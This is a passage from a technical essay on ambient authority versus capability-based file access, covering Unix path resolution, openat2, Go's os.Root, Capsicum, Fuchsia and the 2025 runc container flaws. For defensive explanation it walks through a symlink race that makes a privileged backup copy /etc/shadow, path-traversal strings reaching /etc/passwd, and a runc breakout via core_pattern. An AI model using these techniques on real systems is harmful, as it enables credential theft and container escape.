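Alternatively, a launcher can open the two files and pass their descriptors to the converter. One column of the table lists what the interface requires, meaning the authority the converter needs to serve any request it might receive.

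| Design | Pairs the task needs | Pairs the interface requires | Pairs the converter can reach |
|---|---|---|---|
| Paths, full access to the store | 2 | 100,000 | 100,000 |
| Paths, with sources and outputs separated | 2 | 50,000 | 50,000 |
| Descriptors, account unchanged | 2 | 2 | 100,000 |
| Descriptors, account stripped of file access | 2 | 2 | 2 |

Reviewers are most likely to approve the third design too early. It passes the substitution test, because a user can no longer make the converter open a file by naming it. But if a malicious document exploits a bug in the converter, the attacker can still open all 50,000 files. The redesign made it possible to remove the converter's other rights but, as with `cat`, somebody still has to remove them.

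Amazon's storage service has offered something close to the last design, at least for reading. Its Object Lambda feature runs a customer's function to transform a file as someone retrieves it. AWS gives the function a pre-signed URL for the original file, signed with the requester's identity rather than the function's own role. By default, the URL expires after 61 seconds.

Reviewers should count needed pairs for each request, because the next user will ask for two different files. Over a year the converter might legitimately use every file in the store, and an administrator who writes a fixed policy in advance has to allow for that. Miller and colleagues make this criticism of most sandboxes in their 2005 paper, arguing that nobody knows beforehand what a program will need and that its needs change as it runs. It also matters whether simultaneous requests share a process. If one process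 handles 20 conversions, each with its own two files, a malicious document can reach 40 pairs, compared with two if each conversion has its own process.

The count treats all pairs as equal, but overwriting the payroll file does more harm than reading the canteen menu, so removing one dangerous pair could matter more than removing 50,000 harmless ones. Miller and colleagues suggest picturing the table of programs and resources with each row's height proportional to the chance that the program is corrupted or confused, and each column's width proportional to the damage an attacker could do with that resource. The filled-in area then approximates the system's exposure to attack. They don't draw such a table, because the knowledge needed to set the sizes is "largely inaccessible". A reviewer can at least list the few worst pairs separately and check whether a redesign removes them.

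The count also leaves out what a program can do through other programs. In a mailing-list exchange between Nicol, Karp and Miller (2026), Karp gave the example of a service that updates a database when someone calls it. Suppose the converter in the last design can also call an indexing service, which can write to all 50,000 files. If the indexing service might do anything it is asked, the converter can reach one read and 50,000 writes, or 50,001 pairs of files and operations. If the service's code only updates one index file in the store, the converter can reach three pairs, the original two plus a write to the index.

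Miller and Shapiro distinguish these two ways of setting a limit. The larger figure depends only on the arrangement of permissions. It can reliably show that a program cannot reach something, but not that it can. The smaller figure also depends on how the intermediate program behaves. *Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016) proposed formal definitions of permission and authority, with bounds of both kinds, for a small object-oriented language. An ordinary review only needs to record which figure the count uses and, if the answer was three, to count again when somebody changes the indexing service.

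## Why designers leave authority ambient

Most programmers would write a document converter that takes file paths, although it would need far less authority if it received open file handles. The interfaces they inherit are built around paths and user accounts, and passing handles takes extra work. The administrators who run their programs also have good reasons to prefer rules about what each person can access.

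### The user as the unit of protection

Ambient authority suited the time-sharing systems of the 1960s and 1970s, where many people used one computer and needed protection from each other. Saltzer and Schroeder define the user of such a system as the person accountable for what a running program does. The system labelled each running program with that person's identifier and looked it up in a list kept with each file. They compare this to a store clerk who checks a customer's name against a list of people with credit. A ticket-based system, like a lock that opens for any matching key, checks the ticket but not how the program got it, so it is harder to establish which person is accountable.

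Treating a program as its user makes sense if the user wrote it. Miller and colleagues call this a simplifying assumption. When a user opens a spreadsheet in Excel, the system treats both the spreadsheet and Excel as faithful extensions of her intent, although she wrote neither. Saltzer and Schroeder had already pointed out in 1975 that a borrowed program can use every right its borrower has. They thought that writing or fully auditing every program in-house would be an "unbearable economic burden" for most organisations. They proposed running borrowed programs separately, with only the rights the programs needed, but only a few of the most advanced systems of the time tried to let users arrange this.

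Efficiency also affected what programmers saw. Searching a list takes longer than checking a ticket, so most real systems used both. They checked a list at the user interface, then issued a temporary ticket that the lower-level machinery could check quickly. `open()` followed by `read()` follows the same pattern. Some designers also shortened the lists. One popular system simplified storage by allowing only three entries per file, for the file's creator, one group and everybody. Unix still divides its basic file permissions this way, and none of the three entries can refer to a particular program.

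Some researchers tried to build whole systems on capabilities. In 1968 the University of California at Berkeley began work on CAL-TSS, which was meant to serve several hundred users. *Reflections on an Operating System Design* (Lampson and Sturgis, 1976) lists capability-based protection among the system's distinctive features. According to *Early Capability Architectures*, a chapter by Henry Levy, Berkeley abandoned the system in 1971 because it could not meet its goals for service and performance. Design flaws were partly to blame, but so was the hardware, which had little main memory and only one pair of registers for managing it. A similar project at the University of Chicago ran out of money before it was finished. These failures left later designers without a large working system to copy, though they are weak evidence against capabilities themselves.

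### Names that people can keep

The word "capability" comes from a 1966 design by Dennis and Van Horn, in which a process refers to a file by its position in the process's own list of capabilities. That number would be useless to a colleague, just as a Unix file descriptor number would be. *Early Capability Architectures* points out that people need names they can remember and need to share and keep files. A person can put a file path in a manual, read it out over the phone or save it in a settings file.

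Even passing a capability to someone requires a name for the recipient. In Saltzer and Schroeder's example, Doe wants to give Smith access to a new file and must first learn Smith's name in the system, perhaps by having Smith shout it down the hall.

Names also outlast the processes that use them. A process loses its open descriptors when it ends, so a program that will need the same file later usually saves the path, and then needs standing permission to open it. CAL-TSS had a severe version of this problem because it could not save its lists of capabilities to disk without compromising its protection.

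None of this requires the program to have ambient authority. Dennis and Van Horn's design included directories that paired each text name with a capability. At login, the system gave the user's first process a capability for the user's root directory, where it could look up a name and get the paired capability. People can keep using names as long as something turns them into handles. A program that does this itself needs access to the whole directory, but if a launcher does it, as the shell does for `cat`, the program needs only the resulting handle.

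### A log file five calls down

Passing handles also takes work inside a program. In this Python example, the main program calls `run`, and four calls further down, `round_price` writes a line to a log file:

```python
def run(order):
    return price_order(order)

def price_order(order):
    return sum(price_item(item) for item in order)

def price_item(item):
    return add_tax(item.price)

def add_tax(price):
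    return round_price(price * 1.2)

def round_price(amount):
    with open("shop.log", "a") as log:
        log.write(f"rounding {amount}\n")
    return round(amount, 2)
```

The programmer who added the logging had to change only `round_price`. To pass the log file as a handle instead, they would have to change all five functions:

```python
def run(order, log):
    return price_order(order, log)

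def price_order(order, log):
    return sum(price_item(item, log) for item in order)

def price_item(item, log):
    return add_tax(item.price, log)

def add_tax(price, log):
    return round_price(price * 1.2, log)

def round_price(amount, log):
    log.write(f"rounding {amount}\n")
    return round(amount, 2)

with open("shop.log", "a") as log:
    run(order, log)
```

Four of these functions accept a log only to pass it on. If each belongs to a different library, four maintainers have to change their interfaces, and everyone else who uses those libraries has to supply a log too.

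In return, the main program sets where the log goes, and a test can supply a temporary file. Anyone reading the code can also see that pricing an order writes to a log, which was not apparent in the first version. As with `cat`, though, `round_price` can still call `open()` itself.

A programmer can avoid the extra parameters by connecting the parts beforehand. The setup code creates a rounding object that holds the log, then a tax object that holds the rounding object, and so on up to an object that prices orders. The calls are then as short as in the first version, and only the setup code and the rounding object mention the log. But anyone who receives the pricing object can now cause writes to the log, perhaps without realising it.

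Another shortcut is to put the log, the database connection, the mail client and everything else into one "context" object and pass it to every function. This authority is not ambient, because a function like `round_price` has to select `context.log` to write to the log. But `round_price` also receives the mail client, so it can send email, which it doesn't need to do to round a price.

Old libraries make the work even harder because a library that reads its settings from a fixed path has no parameter through which a caller could pass the file. Miller and colleagues describe how to restrict such software from outside. Polaris, an experimental system from HP Labs, ran an unmodified copy of Excel in a separate account with almost no rights, and gave it access to each spreadsheet as the user opened it. But every part of Excel had the same authority, so even its square-root function could have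 overwritten the spreadsheet. Dividing authority inside a program requires rewriting it, which Miller and colleagues expect to happen one component at a time.

### Needs that are unknown at launch

Even a designer willing to do this work has to know what authority to pass. Miller and colleagues use the card game Solitaire to show how poor the usual choices are. The game needs to draw in its window, receive the player's clicks and keystrokes, and save the score in a file the player chooses.

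If a player runs a game as an ordinary application, the game gets all of the player's authority and could search their email or delete their files. If they run it as an applet, a small program with almost no access to the rest of the computer, it is safe but can't offer to save the score.

A sandbox with a fixed policy is a compromise between the two. Somebody writes a list of permissions, and the system grants them when the game starts. But whoever writes the list doesn't know where the player will want to save the score. Allowing the whole documents folder exposes everything in it, while allowing only a games folder prevents the player from saving anywhere else. Some sandboxes let the player add permissions as the game runs, but Miller and colleagues complain that this produces a "torrent of annoying security dialog boxes".

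One proposal is to grant authority when the user makes a request, "just-in-time" rather than "just-in-case". When a player picks `scores.txt` in a game's save dialog, that choice shows which file the game should write to, so the system can grant access to that file and no others. This adds no work, because the player would have had to choose a file anyway.

This works less well when no request identifies the resource. Miller and colleagues consider email clients the worst case among everyday programs. An email client needs a dangerous combination of rights, and the user would grant some of them, such as access to the mail server, only once, when configuring it. An overnight backup has no user present to choose files, and it must read all of them.

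Some program also has to hold the broad authority that narrow grants are drawn from. In CapDesk, a secure desktop that Miller and colleagues describe, the desktop program holds all of its user's authority. A flaw in that program therefore exposes everything the user has, though a flaw in an application it starts does not.

### The case for central policy

Access lists suit administrators, who usually think in terms of people and jobs, such as who works in payroll and who left last week. In *Perspectives on Security*, Lampson (2015), who helped design the capability system CAL-TSS, recommends lists for long-term policy because they show who can use a resource. He considers capabilities suitable for short-term uses, such as open files.

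In a basic capability system, it is hard to find out who can use a file. Saltzer and Schroeder explain that the file's owner would have to search the whole system for copies of the capability and work out who could reach each one. The owner also couldn't cancel a copy that another user had saved. Designers can add ways to record and revoke access, but an access control list provides both from the start.

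Lists also make staff changes easy to handle. Suppose 40 accountants share 300 files, and each file's list names the accounting group. When an accountant joins or leaves, the administrator adds or removes one name in the group. If each accountant instead held a separate capability for each file, the administrator would have to hand out 300 capabilities when someone joined and cancel 300 when someone left. One capability for a shared folder would reduce that to a single step, but the administrator would still need a way to cancel it for one person without affecting the other 39.

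Many organisations define roles. The designer of a payroll application decides what a payroll clerk may do, and the administrator only has to say who the payroll clerks are. Lampson sees this as an advantage because professionals write the rules, rather than the amateurs who usually configure systems.

Central control also helps in emergencies. Saltzer and Schroeder imagine that a member of a finance department falls ill and a colleague needs the budget file. If only the absent employee can change the file's access list, the manager can't give the colleague access. They propose giving a department administrator the power to change any access list in the department. They worry that this power is unchecked, and suggest safeguards such as a one-day delay or a second person's approval. A system that relied only on handles held by individuals would also have trouble with absent employees, unless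 somebody had arranged for a spare handle.

Buyers rarely push designers for more security. Lampson argues that people don't buy security because the danger is small enough that they prefer more features, and because security takes work to configure and stops them from doing things. By the same reasoning, a company that pays programmers to pass handles through every function spends the money immediately, to prevent an accident that might never have happened.

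Lampson lists capabilities among the ideas that have failed, "except short term". But he counts an idea as having worked roughly if it was widely adopted, and his successes include passwords, so the list is better evidence of what designers chose than of what protects people.

He also criticizes access control in general, which he says "doesn't work" after 40 years of experience. He argues that its purpose is to deny access, which stops people from doing their work. They then relax the rules, usually too much, and nobody notices until there is a disaster. He adds that administrators want detailed policies but can manage only coarse ones. As an example of complicated configuration, he cites printing in Windows, which he says involves 12 levels of indirection, each with its own security.

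Miller and colleagues object that no central authority could know enough to give every program only what it needs, because those needs depend on what each part of each program is doing. An administrator can know that Alice works in accounts, but not that the report program she just started needs one particular spreadsheet.

An organisation can combine the two positions. It can keep its lists and roles to decide which files Alice may use, and pass the report program only the spreadsheet she selects. In Miller and colleagues' own example, an imaginary organisation has ordinary user accounts, and one employee uses CapDesk and Polaris to divide his authority among his programs. The case for central policy is therefore a good reason to keep access lists for people, but it does not show that every program needs all of its user's authority.

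### What builders of capability systems report

Ambient authority also causes problems that grow over time. Hardy's rule for opening a file at Tymshare reached fourteen "ands" and "ors" through one exception after another. Each clause that allowed more access created security problems in previously secure programs, and each restriction broke programs with legitimate uses.

Before building a capability system, Hardy and his colleagues feared that capabilities would take up most of its storage. He reports that their systems were usually smaller than comparable ones based on access lists, because capabilities replaced many separate mechanisms for naming and protection. He gives no measurements, and he had an interest in the result because he was the senior architect of the company behind KeyKOS, one of these systems.

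Hardy also warned that systems that added capabilities to traditional mechanisms sometimes suffered more from the combined disadvantages than they gained from the combined advantages. He doesn't name these systems or explain what went wrong. Saltzer and Schroeder, by contrast, considered a mixture of access control lists and capabilities the most practical compromise, and Miller and colleagues' approach requires old and new software to coexist while people replace the old.

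How the two mechanisms are combined probably matters. In Saltzer and Schroeder's mixture, the system uses the list to determine whether to issue a capability, and the program then uses the capability. A hybrid is more dangerous if a program can use either mechanism for the same task. If a document converter gains a parameter for an open file but keeps the old one for a path, a reviewer has to check both, and an attacker can still use the path.

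Microsoft's experimental operating system Midori had no ambient authority. Joe Duffy, who worked on it, explains that each program came with a manifest of what it needed. The system decided what to grant and passed it to the program's main function as objects. Code could use a file only if it had received an object for that file.

The language also banned mutable global variables, because a programmer could have stored the whole file system in one and made it available everywhere. There was no global function for reading the time, so code that needed the time had to request a `Clock` object. These restrictions had benefits beyond security. A static function with no access to a clock or to input and output always gives the same result for the same arguments, so the system could save the result or even compute it at compile time. Duffy says the ban on mutable globals also made the system more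 reliable, though he found the improvement hard to quantify.

Developers needed time to get used to passing capabilities explicitly. Duffy says that "big bags" of capabilities commonly grew over time, much like the context object in the pricing example. Developers also had to decide when to pass a capability. They could give a `Stopwatch` a `Clock` each time they started or stopped it, or once when they created it. The second option made the stopwatch easier to share, but anyone who received it could then read the time. An object that needed 15 capabilities might require a constructor with 15 arguments, which Duffy calls "unwieldy" and "annoying". He recommends grouping related capabilities. The team had these difficulties even though it included some of the original designers of KeyKOS and its successors.

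Midori never had much real-world use. Duffy says the team focused less on how users would manage permissions than on the architecture. He doubts, for example, that his mother would want to be asked whether a program may use a clock. As far as the team knew, nobody broke into the few decoy systems it set up to attract attackers, but he says the team never got to prove the design at scale.

These accounts are thin evidence about how developers cope without ambient authority. Hardy and Duffy both describe systems they helped to build, and neither compares similar teams working with and without ambient authority. Their accounts show that people can build such systems and describe some of the difficulties, but not how much extra time the work takes or how many security faults it prevents.

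### When to keep ambient authority

Ambient authority is sometimes good enough. Miller and colleagues say that excess authority within an organisation creates few vulnerabilities if the organisation is small, if little is at stake, or if nobody in it can be corrupted or confused. For a single program, it is reasonable to keep ambient authority under these conditions:

- All requests come from one party, and the program has no rights that this party lacks.
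- The program has one purpose, and its account can do little else.
- The names it uses come from that party or from its own code, and not from documents, messages or web pages that other people wrote.
- A mistake or a successful attack would do little harm, for example because there are backups.

A script that somebody writes to rename their own holiday photos meets all four. Passing it a handle for each photo would waste effort.

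A program that fails one condition may still be safe. For example, a nightly job might total a shop's sales using an account that can only read the sales table and write to one summary. A wrong total could cost the shop money, but handles would hardly help, because the job has no other table to confuse with the right one.

A program can safely accept file names from strangers if its account can only read public files, because it can't return anything they couldn't have read themselves. The danger comes from combining outside names with rights that the requester lacks, as Hardy's compiler did. If a program does this with valuable resources, the designer should pass handles instead of names, or at least select a credential that belongs to the requester.

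These conditions can fail even if the program doesn't change, as they did when Tymshare widened the compiler's permissions. The photo script would no longer meet them if its owner put it behind a web page so that relatives could rename photos too. A designer who keeps ambient authority should write down the conditions that make it safe, preferably next to the account's permissions, where an administrator will see them before granting more.

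## Names or handles in operating-system interfaces

A program that takes names from outsiders and has rights they lack needs a safer way to reach files, processes and network connections. Operating systems offer several, which differ mainly in what the program can still name afterwards. Files need the most care because the system resolves a path in several steps, and another program can interfere between steps.

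### How a path becomes a file

When a program opens `/srv/drop/report.txt`, the operating system's kernel handles the request. It looks up `srv` in the root directory, `/`, then `drop` in `srv`, then `report.txt` in `drop`. At each directory, it checks that the program's account may search there. Each directory entry binds a name to a file or directory, and anyone who may write to the directory containing the entry can usually replace that binding.

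Two kinds of directory entry can lead a path lookup somewhere unexpected. The entry `..` leads to the parent directory, so `/srv/drop/../../etc/passwd` leads to `/etc/passwd`. A symbolic link holds another path as text, and the kernel follows that path when it reaches the link. Users can create a symbolic link to a file they cannot access, so a user who can write to `/srv/drop` can put a link there to `/etc/shadow`, a file of hashed passwords that ordinary users cannot read.

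The kernel repeats the walk every time a program passes it a path. If a program first checks a path and then opens it, the two walks can end at different files, a fault called a time-of-check to time-of-use race. In the example below, a backup program runs as the administrator, copies reports from a folder that users can write to, and is supposed to refuse links.

| Step | Backup program | Attacker |
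|---|---|---|
| 1 | `lstat("/srv/drop/report.txt")` finds an ordinary file | |
| 2 | | `unlink("/srv/drop/report.txt")` removes it |
| 3 | | `symlink("/etc/shadow", "/srv/drop/report.txt")` puts a link in its place |
| 4 | `open("/srv/drop/report.txt", O_RDONLY)` follows the link and opens `/etc/shadow` | |
| 5 | `read()` and `write()` copy the password hashes into the backup | |

Both checks were correct, because the file was ordinary at step 1 and the administrator is allowed to read `/etc/shadow` at step 4. If users can read the backups of their own reports, the attacker can now read the password hashes.

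In 2026, uutils coreutils, a rewrite of the standard Unix commands in Rust, turned out to have this fault. According to releasealert.dev's *CVE-2026-35359*, the `cp` command used the path to check whether the source was a link, then opened the path in a mode that follows links. An attacker who replaced the file with a link between the check and the open could make a privileged `cp` copy secret files to a place the attacker controlled.

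Rust prevents many memory errors, but its compiler cannot check that two uses of a path reach the same file. Funk (2026), in *uutils coreutils CVEs*, reports that the security firm Zellic audited uutils, a Rust rewrite of the GNU core utilities, and found 113 issues, 44 of which received entries in CVE, the public catalogue of vulnerabilities. Some were races, in which the file a path refers to can change between uses, and these led Canonical, the company behind Ubuntu, to keep the older GNU versions of `cp`, `mv` and `rm` in Ubuntu 26.04.

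The backup program should open the file first and check it afterwards. With some arguments left out, the calls are:

```
fd = open("/srv/drop/report.txt", O_RDONLY | O_NOFOLLOW)
fstat(fd)
read(fd)
```

`O_NOFOLLOW` makes the first call fail if the last part of the path is a link. `fstat()` then examines the open file, even if the path now leads to a different one, so the program checks and uses the same file. The flag doesn't check earlier parts of the path. If the report is at `/srv/drop/march/report.txt`, the attacker can still replace the directory `march` with a link to another directory.

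### Starting from a directory descriptor

The `openat()` call takes the descriptor of an open directory as well as a path. If the path is relative, the kernel looks it up starting from that directory. If the backup program opens `/srv/drop` once and keeps the descriptor, nobody can redirect the program by replacing `srv` or `drop`, because the kernel no longer looks up those names.

OSV's *CVE-2026-35356* (2026) describes a flaw in the uutils `install` command. With the `-D` option, the command created any missing parent directories, then resolved the path again to create the file instead of using a handle to the directory. An attacker who replaced one of those directories with a symbolic link between the two steps could make the command overwrite a file elsewhere.

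Plain `openat()` does not confine a program to the directory, however. The program can still name every file its account can reach, because the kernel ignores the descriptor if the path is absolute and follows `..` and links even out of the directory. A proposal to the developers of the Go programming language gives this as a reason for wanting something stricter.

A programmer can avoid this by opening the path one component at a time. The program refuses `..`, opens `march` with `O_NOFOLLOW`, and then opens `report.txt` relative to the new descriptor. This works on any Unix system that has `openat()`, but it rejects harmless links along with dangerous ones and protects only the operations where programmers remember to use it. The uutils developers wrote a module that used descriptors this way to prevent races, but they mistakenly limited it to Linux, so their commands stayed vulnerable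 on macOS and FreeBSD, according to Ubuntu's *CVE-2026-35362* (2026).

### Boundaries that the kernel enforces

Linux 5.6 added `openat2()`, which lets the caller restrict the whole walk. The Linux manual page *openat2(2)* describes these flags:

- `RESOLVE_BENEATH` makes the call fail if any step leaves the starting directory. It also rejects absolute paths and absolute links.
- `RESOLVE_IN_ROOT` treats the starting directory as if it were `/`, so absolute paths and surplus `..` components stay inside it.
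- `RESOLVE_NO_SYMLINKS` rejects links anywhere in the path.
- `RESOLVE_NO_MAGICLINKS` rejects special entries, mostly in the `/proc` directory, that behave like links and can lead out of a container.
- `RESOLVE_NO_XDEV` stops the walk from crossing a mount point. This includes bind mounts, which make an existing file or directory appear in a second place.

The next table shows which file each call opens when the program supplies a descriptor for `/data`.

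| Path | `openat()` | `RESOLVE_BENEATH` | `RESOLVE_IN_ROOT` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `a.txt` | `/data/a.txt` | `/data/a.txt` | `/data/a.txt` |
| `../etc/passwd` | `/etc/passwd` | error | `/data/etc/passwd` |
| `/etc/passwd` | `/etc/passwd` | error | `/data/etc/passwd` |
| a link to `/etc/passwd` | `/etc/passwd` | error | `/data/etc/passwd` |

Resolving `..` safely is hard even for the kernel, because someone can move a directory during the walk. Suppose the walk has gone from `/data` down to `/data/sub/deep`, and the next two components are both `..`. If an attacker now moves `deep` into `/scratch`, the first `..` leads to `/scratch` and the second to `/`. The walk has left `/data` without passing back through it, so a check that only stops `..` at `/data` itself misses the escape. When the kernel cannot rule out such an escape, `openat2()` returns the error `EAGAIN`, and the program can try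 again.

These rules are easy to get wrong. According to the Linux manual page, a bug made FreeBSD's earlier flag for the same purpose, `O_BENEATH`, effectively insecure. FreeBSD 13 replaced it with `O_RESOLVE_BENEATH`, which follows the Linux rules.

The flags restrict a single call and not the program. If an attacker takes over the program, the attacker can simply call `open()` instead.

### The runc vulnerabilities of 2025

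The program runc starts containers for Docker and Kubernetes, two widely used systems for running software in isolation. In *runc container breakouts via procfs writes*, Sarai (2025) disclosed three flaws that could let a malicious container take over the machine it ran on. In each, runc looked up a path that the attacker could redirect.

Linux presents many of its settings as files in `/proc`. To hide the dangerous ones from a container, runc covers each with a bind mount of `/dev/null`, a device that discards whatever a program writes to it. runc looked up the container's own `/dev/null` by name. If an attacker replaced that entry with a link to `/proc/sys/kernel/core_pattern`, runc would mount that setting where the container could write to it. After a crash, the kernel runs the program specified in this setting outside the container and with full privileges.

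The error occurred when runc used the name `/dev/null` in a directory tree that the attacker could change. According to a reply on the oss-sec mailing list, a sandboxing program called Syd opens a descriptor for `/dev/null` in advance, so swapping the name later does not affect the descriptor. The second flaw was almost the same, except that the swapped entry was a terminal device that runc mounts as `/dev/console`.

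The third flaw shows that checking a file after opening it isn't enough if the check is too loose. When runc starts a container, it writes a security label to a file under `/proc/self/attr/`, and the label restricts what the container may do. In 2019, researchers found that an attacker could redirect this write to a dummy file, which left the container without its label. The developers responded by checking that the file belonged to `/proc`. The 2025 flaw let an attacker redirect the write to `/proc/self/sched`, which passed the check because it belongs to `/proc`. Writing the label there has no effect, so the container again ran without it. An attacker could also crash the host by redirecting the write to a different file.

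All three attacks require someone to run a container with a custom mount configuration, which might happen when they build or start an untrusted image. The fix took more than 20 patches. The patched runc retried `openat2()` up to 32 times when it returned `EAGAIN`, but some vendors found that containers on busy machines still failed to start. Sarai estimated a failure rate of about 3% in a deliberately harsh test, with all 16 cores of a laptop renaming files in a loop. After a later patch allowed more retries, he saw no failures in over 50,000 tests.

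### Directory handles in Go

Most programmers would rather not assemble these calls themselves. Go 1.24 introduced a type called `os.Root`, which Neil (2025), in *Traversal-resistant file APIs*, explains. A program opens a directory as a root and then uses the root's methods:

```go
root, err := os.OpenRoot("/srv/drop")
f, err := root.Open("march/report.txt")
```

The methods of `os.Root` accept `..` and links that stay inside the root and return an error for those that lead out. On Unix, a root holds a directory descriptor, so it still refers to the same directory after a rename. Neil's rule of thumb is that code that joins a fixed directory to an externally supplied file name should probably use `os.Root`. Archive extraction is a typical case. A command that writes to a location its user types should not use it, because the user may legitimately choose any file.

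`os.Root` gives less protection on some platforms. When Go code runs on JavaScript's file functions, for example, a root holds only the directory's name, so an attacker can still exploit a race by swapping a link. On Unix, a root doesn't stop path lookup from entering a bind mount. Neil justifies this by saying that ordinary users cannot create one. According to comments in Go's source code, a root also doesn't block device files or the special files in `/proc`, so `os.Root` alone would not have been enough for runc. `os.Root` can also be much slower than a normal call on paths with many components.

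As with `cat`, a function that receives only a root can still open any other path, because Go doesn't remove its access to `os.Open`.

### Processes and network connections

Unix identifies each running process by a number, which the system can reuse after the process ends. Suppose a monitoring program records that a worker has number 4312. The worker exits, its parent collects the result, and the system gives 4312 to a database. If the monitor then signals process 4312 to stop, it stops the database. As with paths, the name was correct when recorded but later referred to something else.

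A process descriptor avoids this by referring to one process for as long as the descriptor stays open. Watson, Anderson and colleagues added `pdfork()` to FreeBSD in *Capsicum* (2010). The call creates a process and returns a descriptor for it. The parent can use the descriptor to wait for the process to exit, and closing the descriptor ends the process. A library can also use `pdfork()` to run a helper process without disturbing how the main application manages its own processes.

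Linux has similar descriptors, called pidfds. A program can get one when it creates a process, before the process number could be reassigned. It can also request one by process number, but that number may already be out of date. A pidfd is only partly a handle. It fixes which process the program means, but the right to signal that process remains ambient, because Linux still checks the sender's account before delivering a signal.

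Network addresses and host names are names too, while a connected socket is a handle. For example, a service might fetch web pages for its users but be forbidden to reach the company's internal machines. It looks up `pictures.example`, finds a public address, and then passes the host name to a library that looks it up again. An attacker who controls the record for that name can change it to an internal address between the two lookups. To prevent this, the service should look the name up once, check the address, and connect to that address. Alternatively, a separate program can make the connection and pass the socket on. The receiving program then doesn't need to name an address, although it still can unless something prevents it.

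### Programs that start with only certain directories

The Rust library cap-std aims to keep programs from using paths outside the directories they receive. It replaces the standard file functions with methods on a directory object, and each method accepts only paths that stay below that directory. Some function still has to open the first directory by an ordinary path, and cap-std marks such functions by requiring an extra argument of type `AmbientAuthority`. docs.rs' *Crate ambient_authority* recommends that capability-oriented libraries add this argument to any function that uses ambient authority.

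In Rust's cap-std library, functions that turn an unrestricted path into a handle require an argument created by calling `ambient_authority()`. Reviewers can search for that call to find where a program uses these functions. The requirement doesn't confine hostile code, because any code can make the call and Rust's standard file functions remain available.

WASI, a set of system interfaces for programs compiled to the portable instruction format WebAssembly, goes further and provides no equivalent of plain `open()`. Whoever starts a program gives it directories that are already open, and the program can open files only relative to these directories. It can therefore name only what lies below them, if the software running it enforces the boundary correctly. Neil warns that not all WASI implementations fully do so.

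### Capsicum

Capsicum applies the same idea to ordinary Unix programs. Watson and colleagues added a call, `cap_enter()`, which puts a process into capability mode, where it loses access to the names that all programs share. The paper lists eleven kinds, including file paths, process numbers, network addresses and the names of shared memory. The process can't leave this mode, and any process it creates is in the mode too. The original process keeps the descriptors it already has and can receive more from other processes.

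In Unix, even a file descriptor opened only for reading lets a program change the file's permissions with `fchmod()`. Capsicum therefore lets a program wrap a descriptor in a capability that permits only the operations it lists, chosen from about 60. A program can make a weaker capability from an existing one, but not a stronger one.

A process in capability mode can still use `openat()` to open files below a directory for which it holds a capability. The 2010 version refused every path containing `..`, even harmless ones. Watson and colleagues had considered allowing paths that stayed inside the directory, but they chose the simplest rule and accepted less flexibility because two cooperating sandboxes could have escaped by moving directories during the path lookup.

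They converted four programs:

| Program | Purpose | Change |
|---|---|---|
| `tcpdump` | displays network traffic | 2 lines to enter capability mode, about 10 with limits on its descriptors |
| `dhclient` | obtains a network address | 2 lines |
| `gzip` | compresses files | 409 lines, about 16% of its source code |
| Chromium | web browser | about 100 lines |

`tcpdump` needed only a small change because it already opens what it needs at the start and then processes data in a loop, so the programmers could insert `cap_enter()` just before the loop. Chromium also needed only a small change because it already ran each page's code in a separate process. Its Windows sandbox, by comparison, took 22,350 lines, most of which forwarded blocked system calls to a trusted process. `gzip` was not divided into processes this way, so the programmers had to divide it and pass descriptors between the parts.

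Even `tcpdump` depended on names that did not appear in its own code. In capability mode, it could not turn network addresses into host names, because a system library waited until the first lookup to open its settings file by path. The programmers had a separate local program do the lookups instead. The new version of `gzip` seemed to run faster than the old one until they discovered that the compression level, a global variable, was not reaching the sandboxed process.

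The measured slowdowns were mostly small. Using a wrapped descriptor added about 0.06 microseconds to a call, or between 4% and 10% in simple tests. Watson and colleagues could not measure any slowdown in `tcpdump` or `dhclient`. Starting a sandbox added 2.37 milliseconds to each run of `gzip`, which matters for tiny files, but at about 512 kilobytes the run times with and without the sandbox were within 5% of each other. Watson and colleagues designed the system and took these measurements themselves, using a prototype on 2010 hardware. They considered programming effort a bigger problem than speed, because dividing a program between processes makes it harder to write and debug.

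The free-software news site LWN described FreeBSD's early support for Capsicum as experimental. FreeBSD has included Capsicum in its standard kernel since version 10, and programs now use `cap_rights_limit()` to limit a descriptor's rights. If a program limits a directory's descriptor, any file it then opens through that descriptor has the same limits. A program that hasn't been written or modified to use Capsicum still runs with its user's full authority.

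### Fuchsia

In Google's Fuchsia operating system, a process starts without the shared names that Capsicum takes away from a running process. It can use only the objects for which it holds handles, and it gets its first handles from the program that created it. Each handle carries a set of rights, and a program can pass on a copy with fewer rights.

Fuchsia programs still use file paths, but they share no root directory. Each process has its own table, in which a prefix such as `/data` stands for a directory handle. A path with no matching prefix cannot be resolved, and the same path can refer to different files in two programs. A directory handle also gives no access to the parent directory. The drawback is that software written for another system's calls has to be adapted first.

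### Shapiro's objection about rebinding

Jonathan Shapiro, who co-wrote the 2003 paper on capability myths, thinks capabilities would not remove most of this trouble. Karp (2026), in *String processing errors*, had asked the capability researchers' mailing list whether capabilities defend better than cleaning up strings when someone with access to `/data` asks for `/data/../etc/passwd`. Shapiro replied on 14 April that Unix does use ambient authority at each step as it walks a path, but argued that an attacker could cause almost any of the same problems by changing what names refer to. Directory entries can change before, during or after the walk, so the same path can give different results, and he pointed out that this also happens in capability systems.

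A program can reach the wrong file even if it holds the directory as a capability. If it looks up `template.txt` in that directory, checks the file, and then looks up the name again, it can get a different file. To avoid this, the program has to keep the result of the first lookup and use that.

The objection is weaker when the attacker gains access to something new. A symbolic link is text, so the attacker can bind `report.txt` to `/etc/shadow` without being able to read that file. The backup program then reads it using its own account's permissions. In a capability system, directory entries hold capabilities, so an attacker can add only capabilities they already have. The backup program might save the wrong data, but it would not read a secret file for the attacker. The theft of `/etc/shadow` required both a name that the attacker could rebind and a program with ambient authority over the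 new target, so removing either one would have stopped it. Similarly, Sarai advises running runc without administrator rights, because most of the redirected writes then fail.

Karp later proposed that Alice, who owns `/data`, keep a table that matches strings to capabilities. Bob receives a capability when he asks for `foo.txt`, but nothing when he asks for `../etc/passwd`, because that string is not in the table. Richard Gibson asked what this adds, since the code to reject the bad path seemed to be the same either way. Karp answered that Bob could previously construct a new path, but now he can only select from a fixed set. Niki Aimable Niyikiza, whose article on path strings had prompted the discussion, agreed that this is an improvement, but only if nothing besides Alice's table interprets the string. If the table holds paths and the program passes them to the Unix kernel, the kernel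 interprets them again and the race returns. The table should therefore hold open file descriptors.

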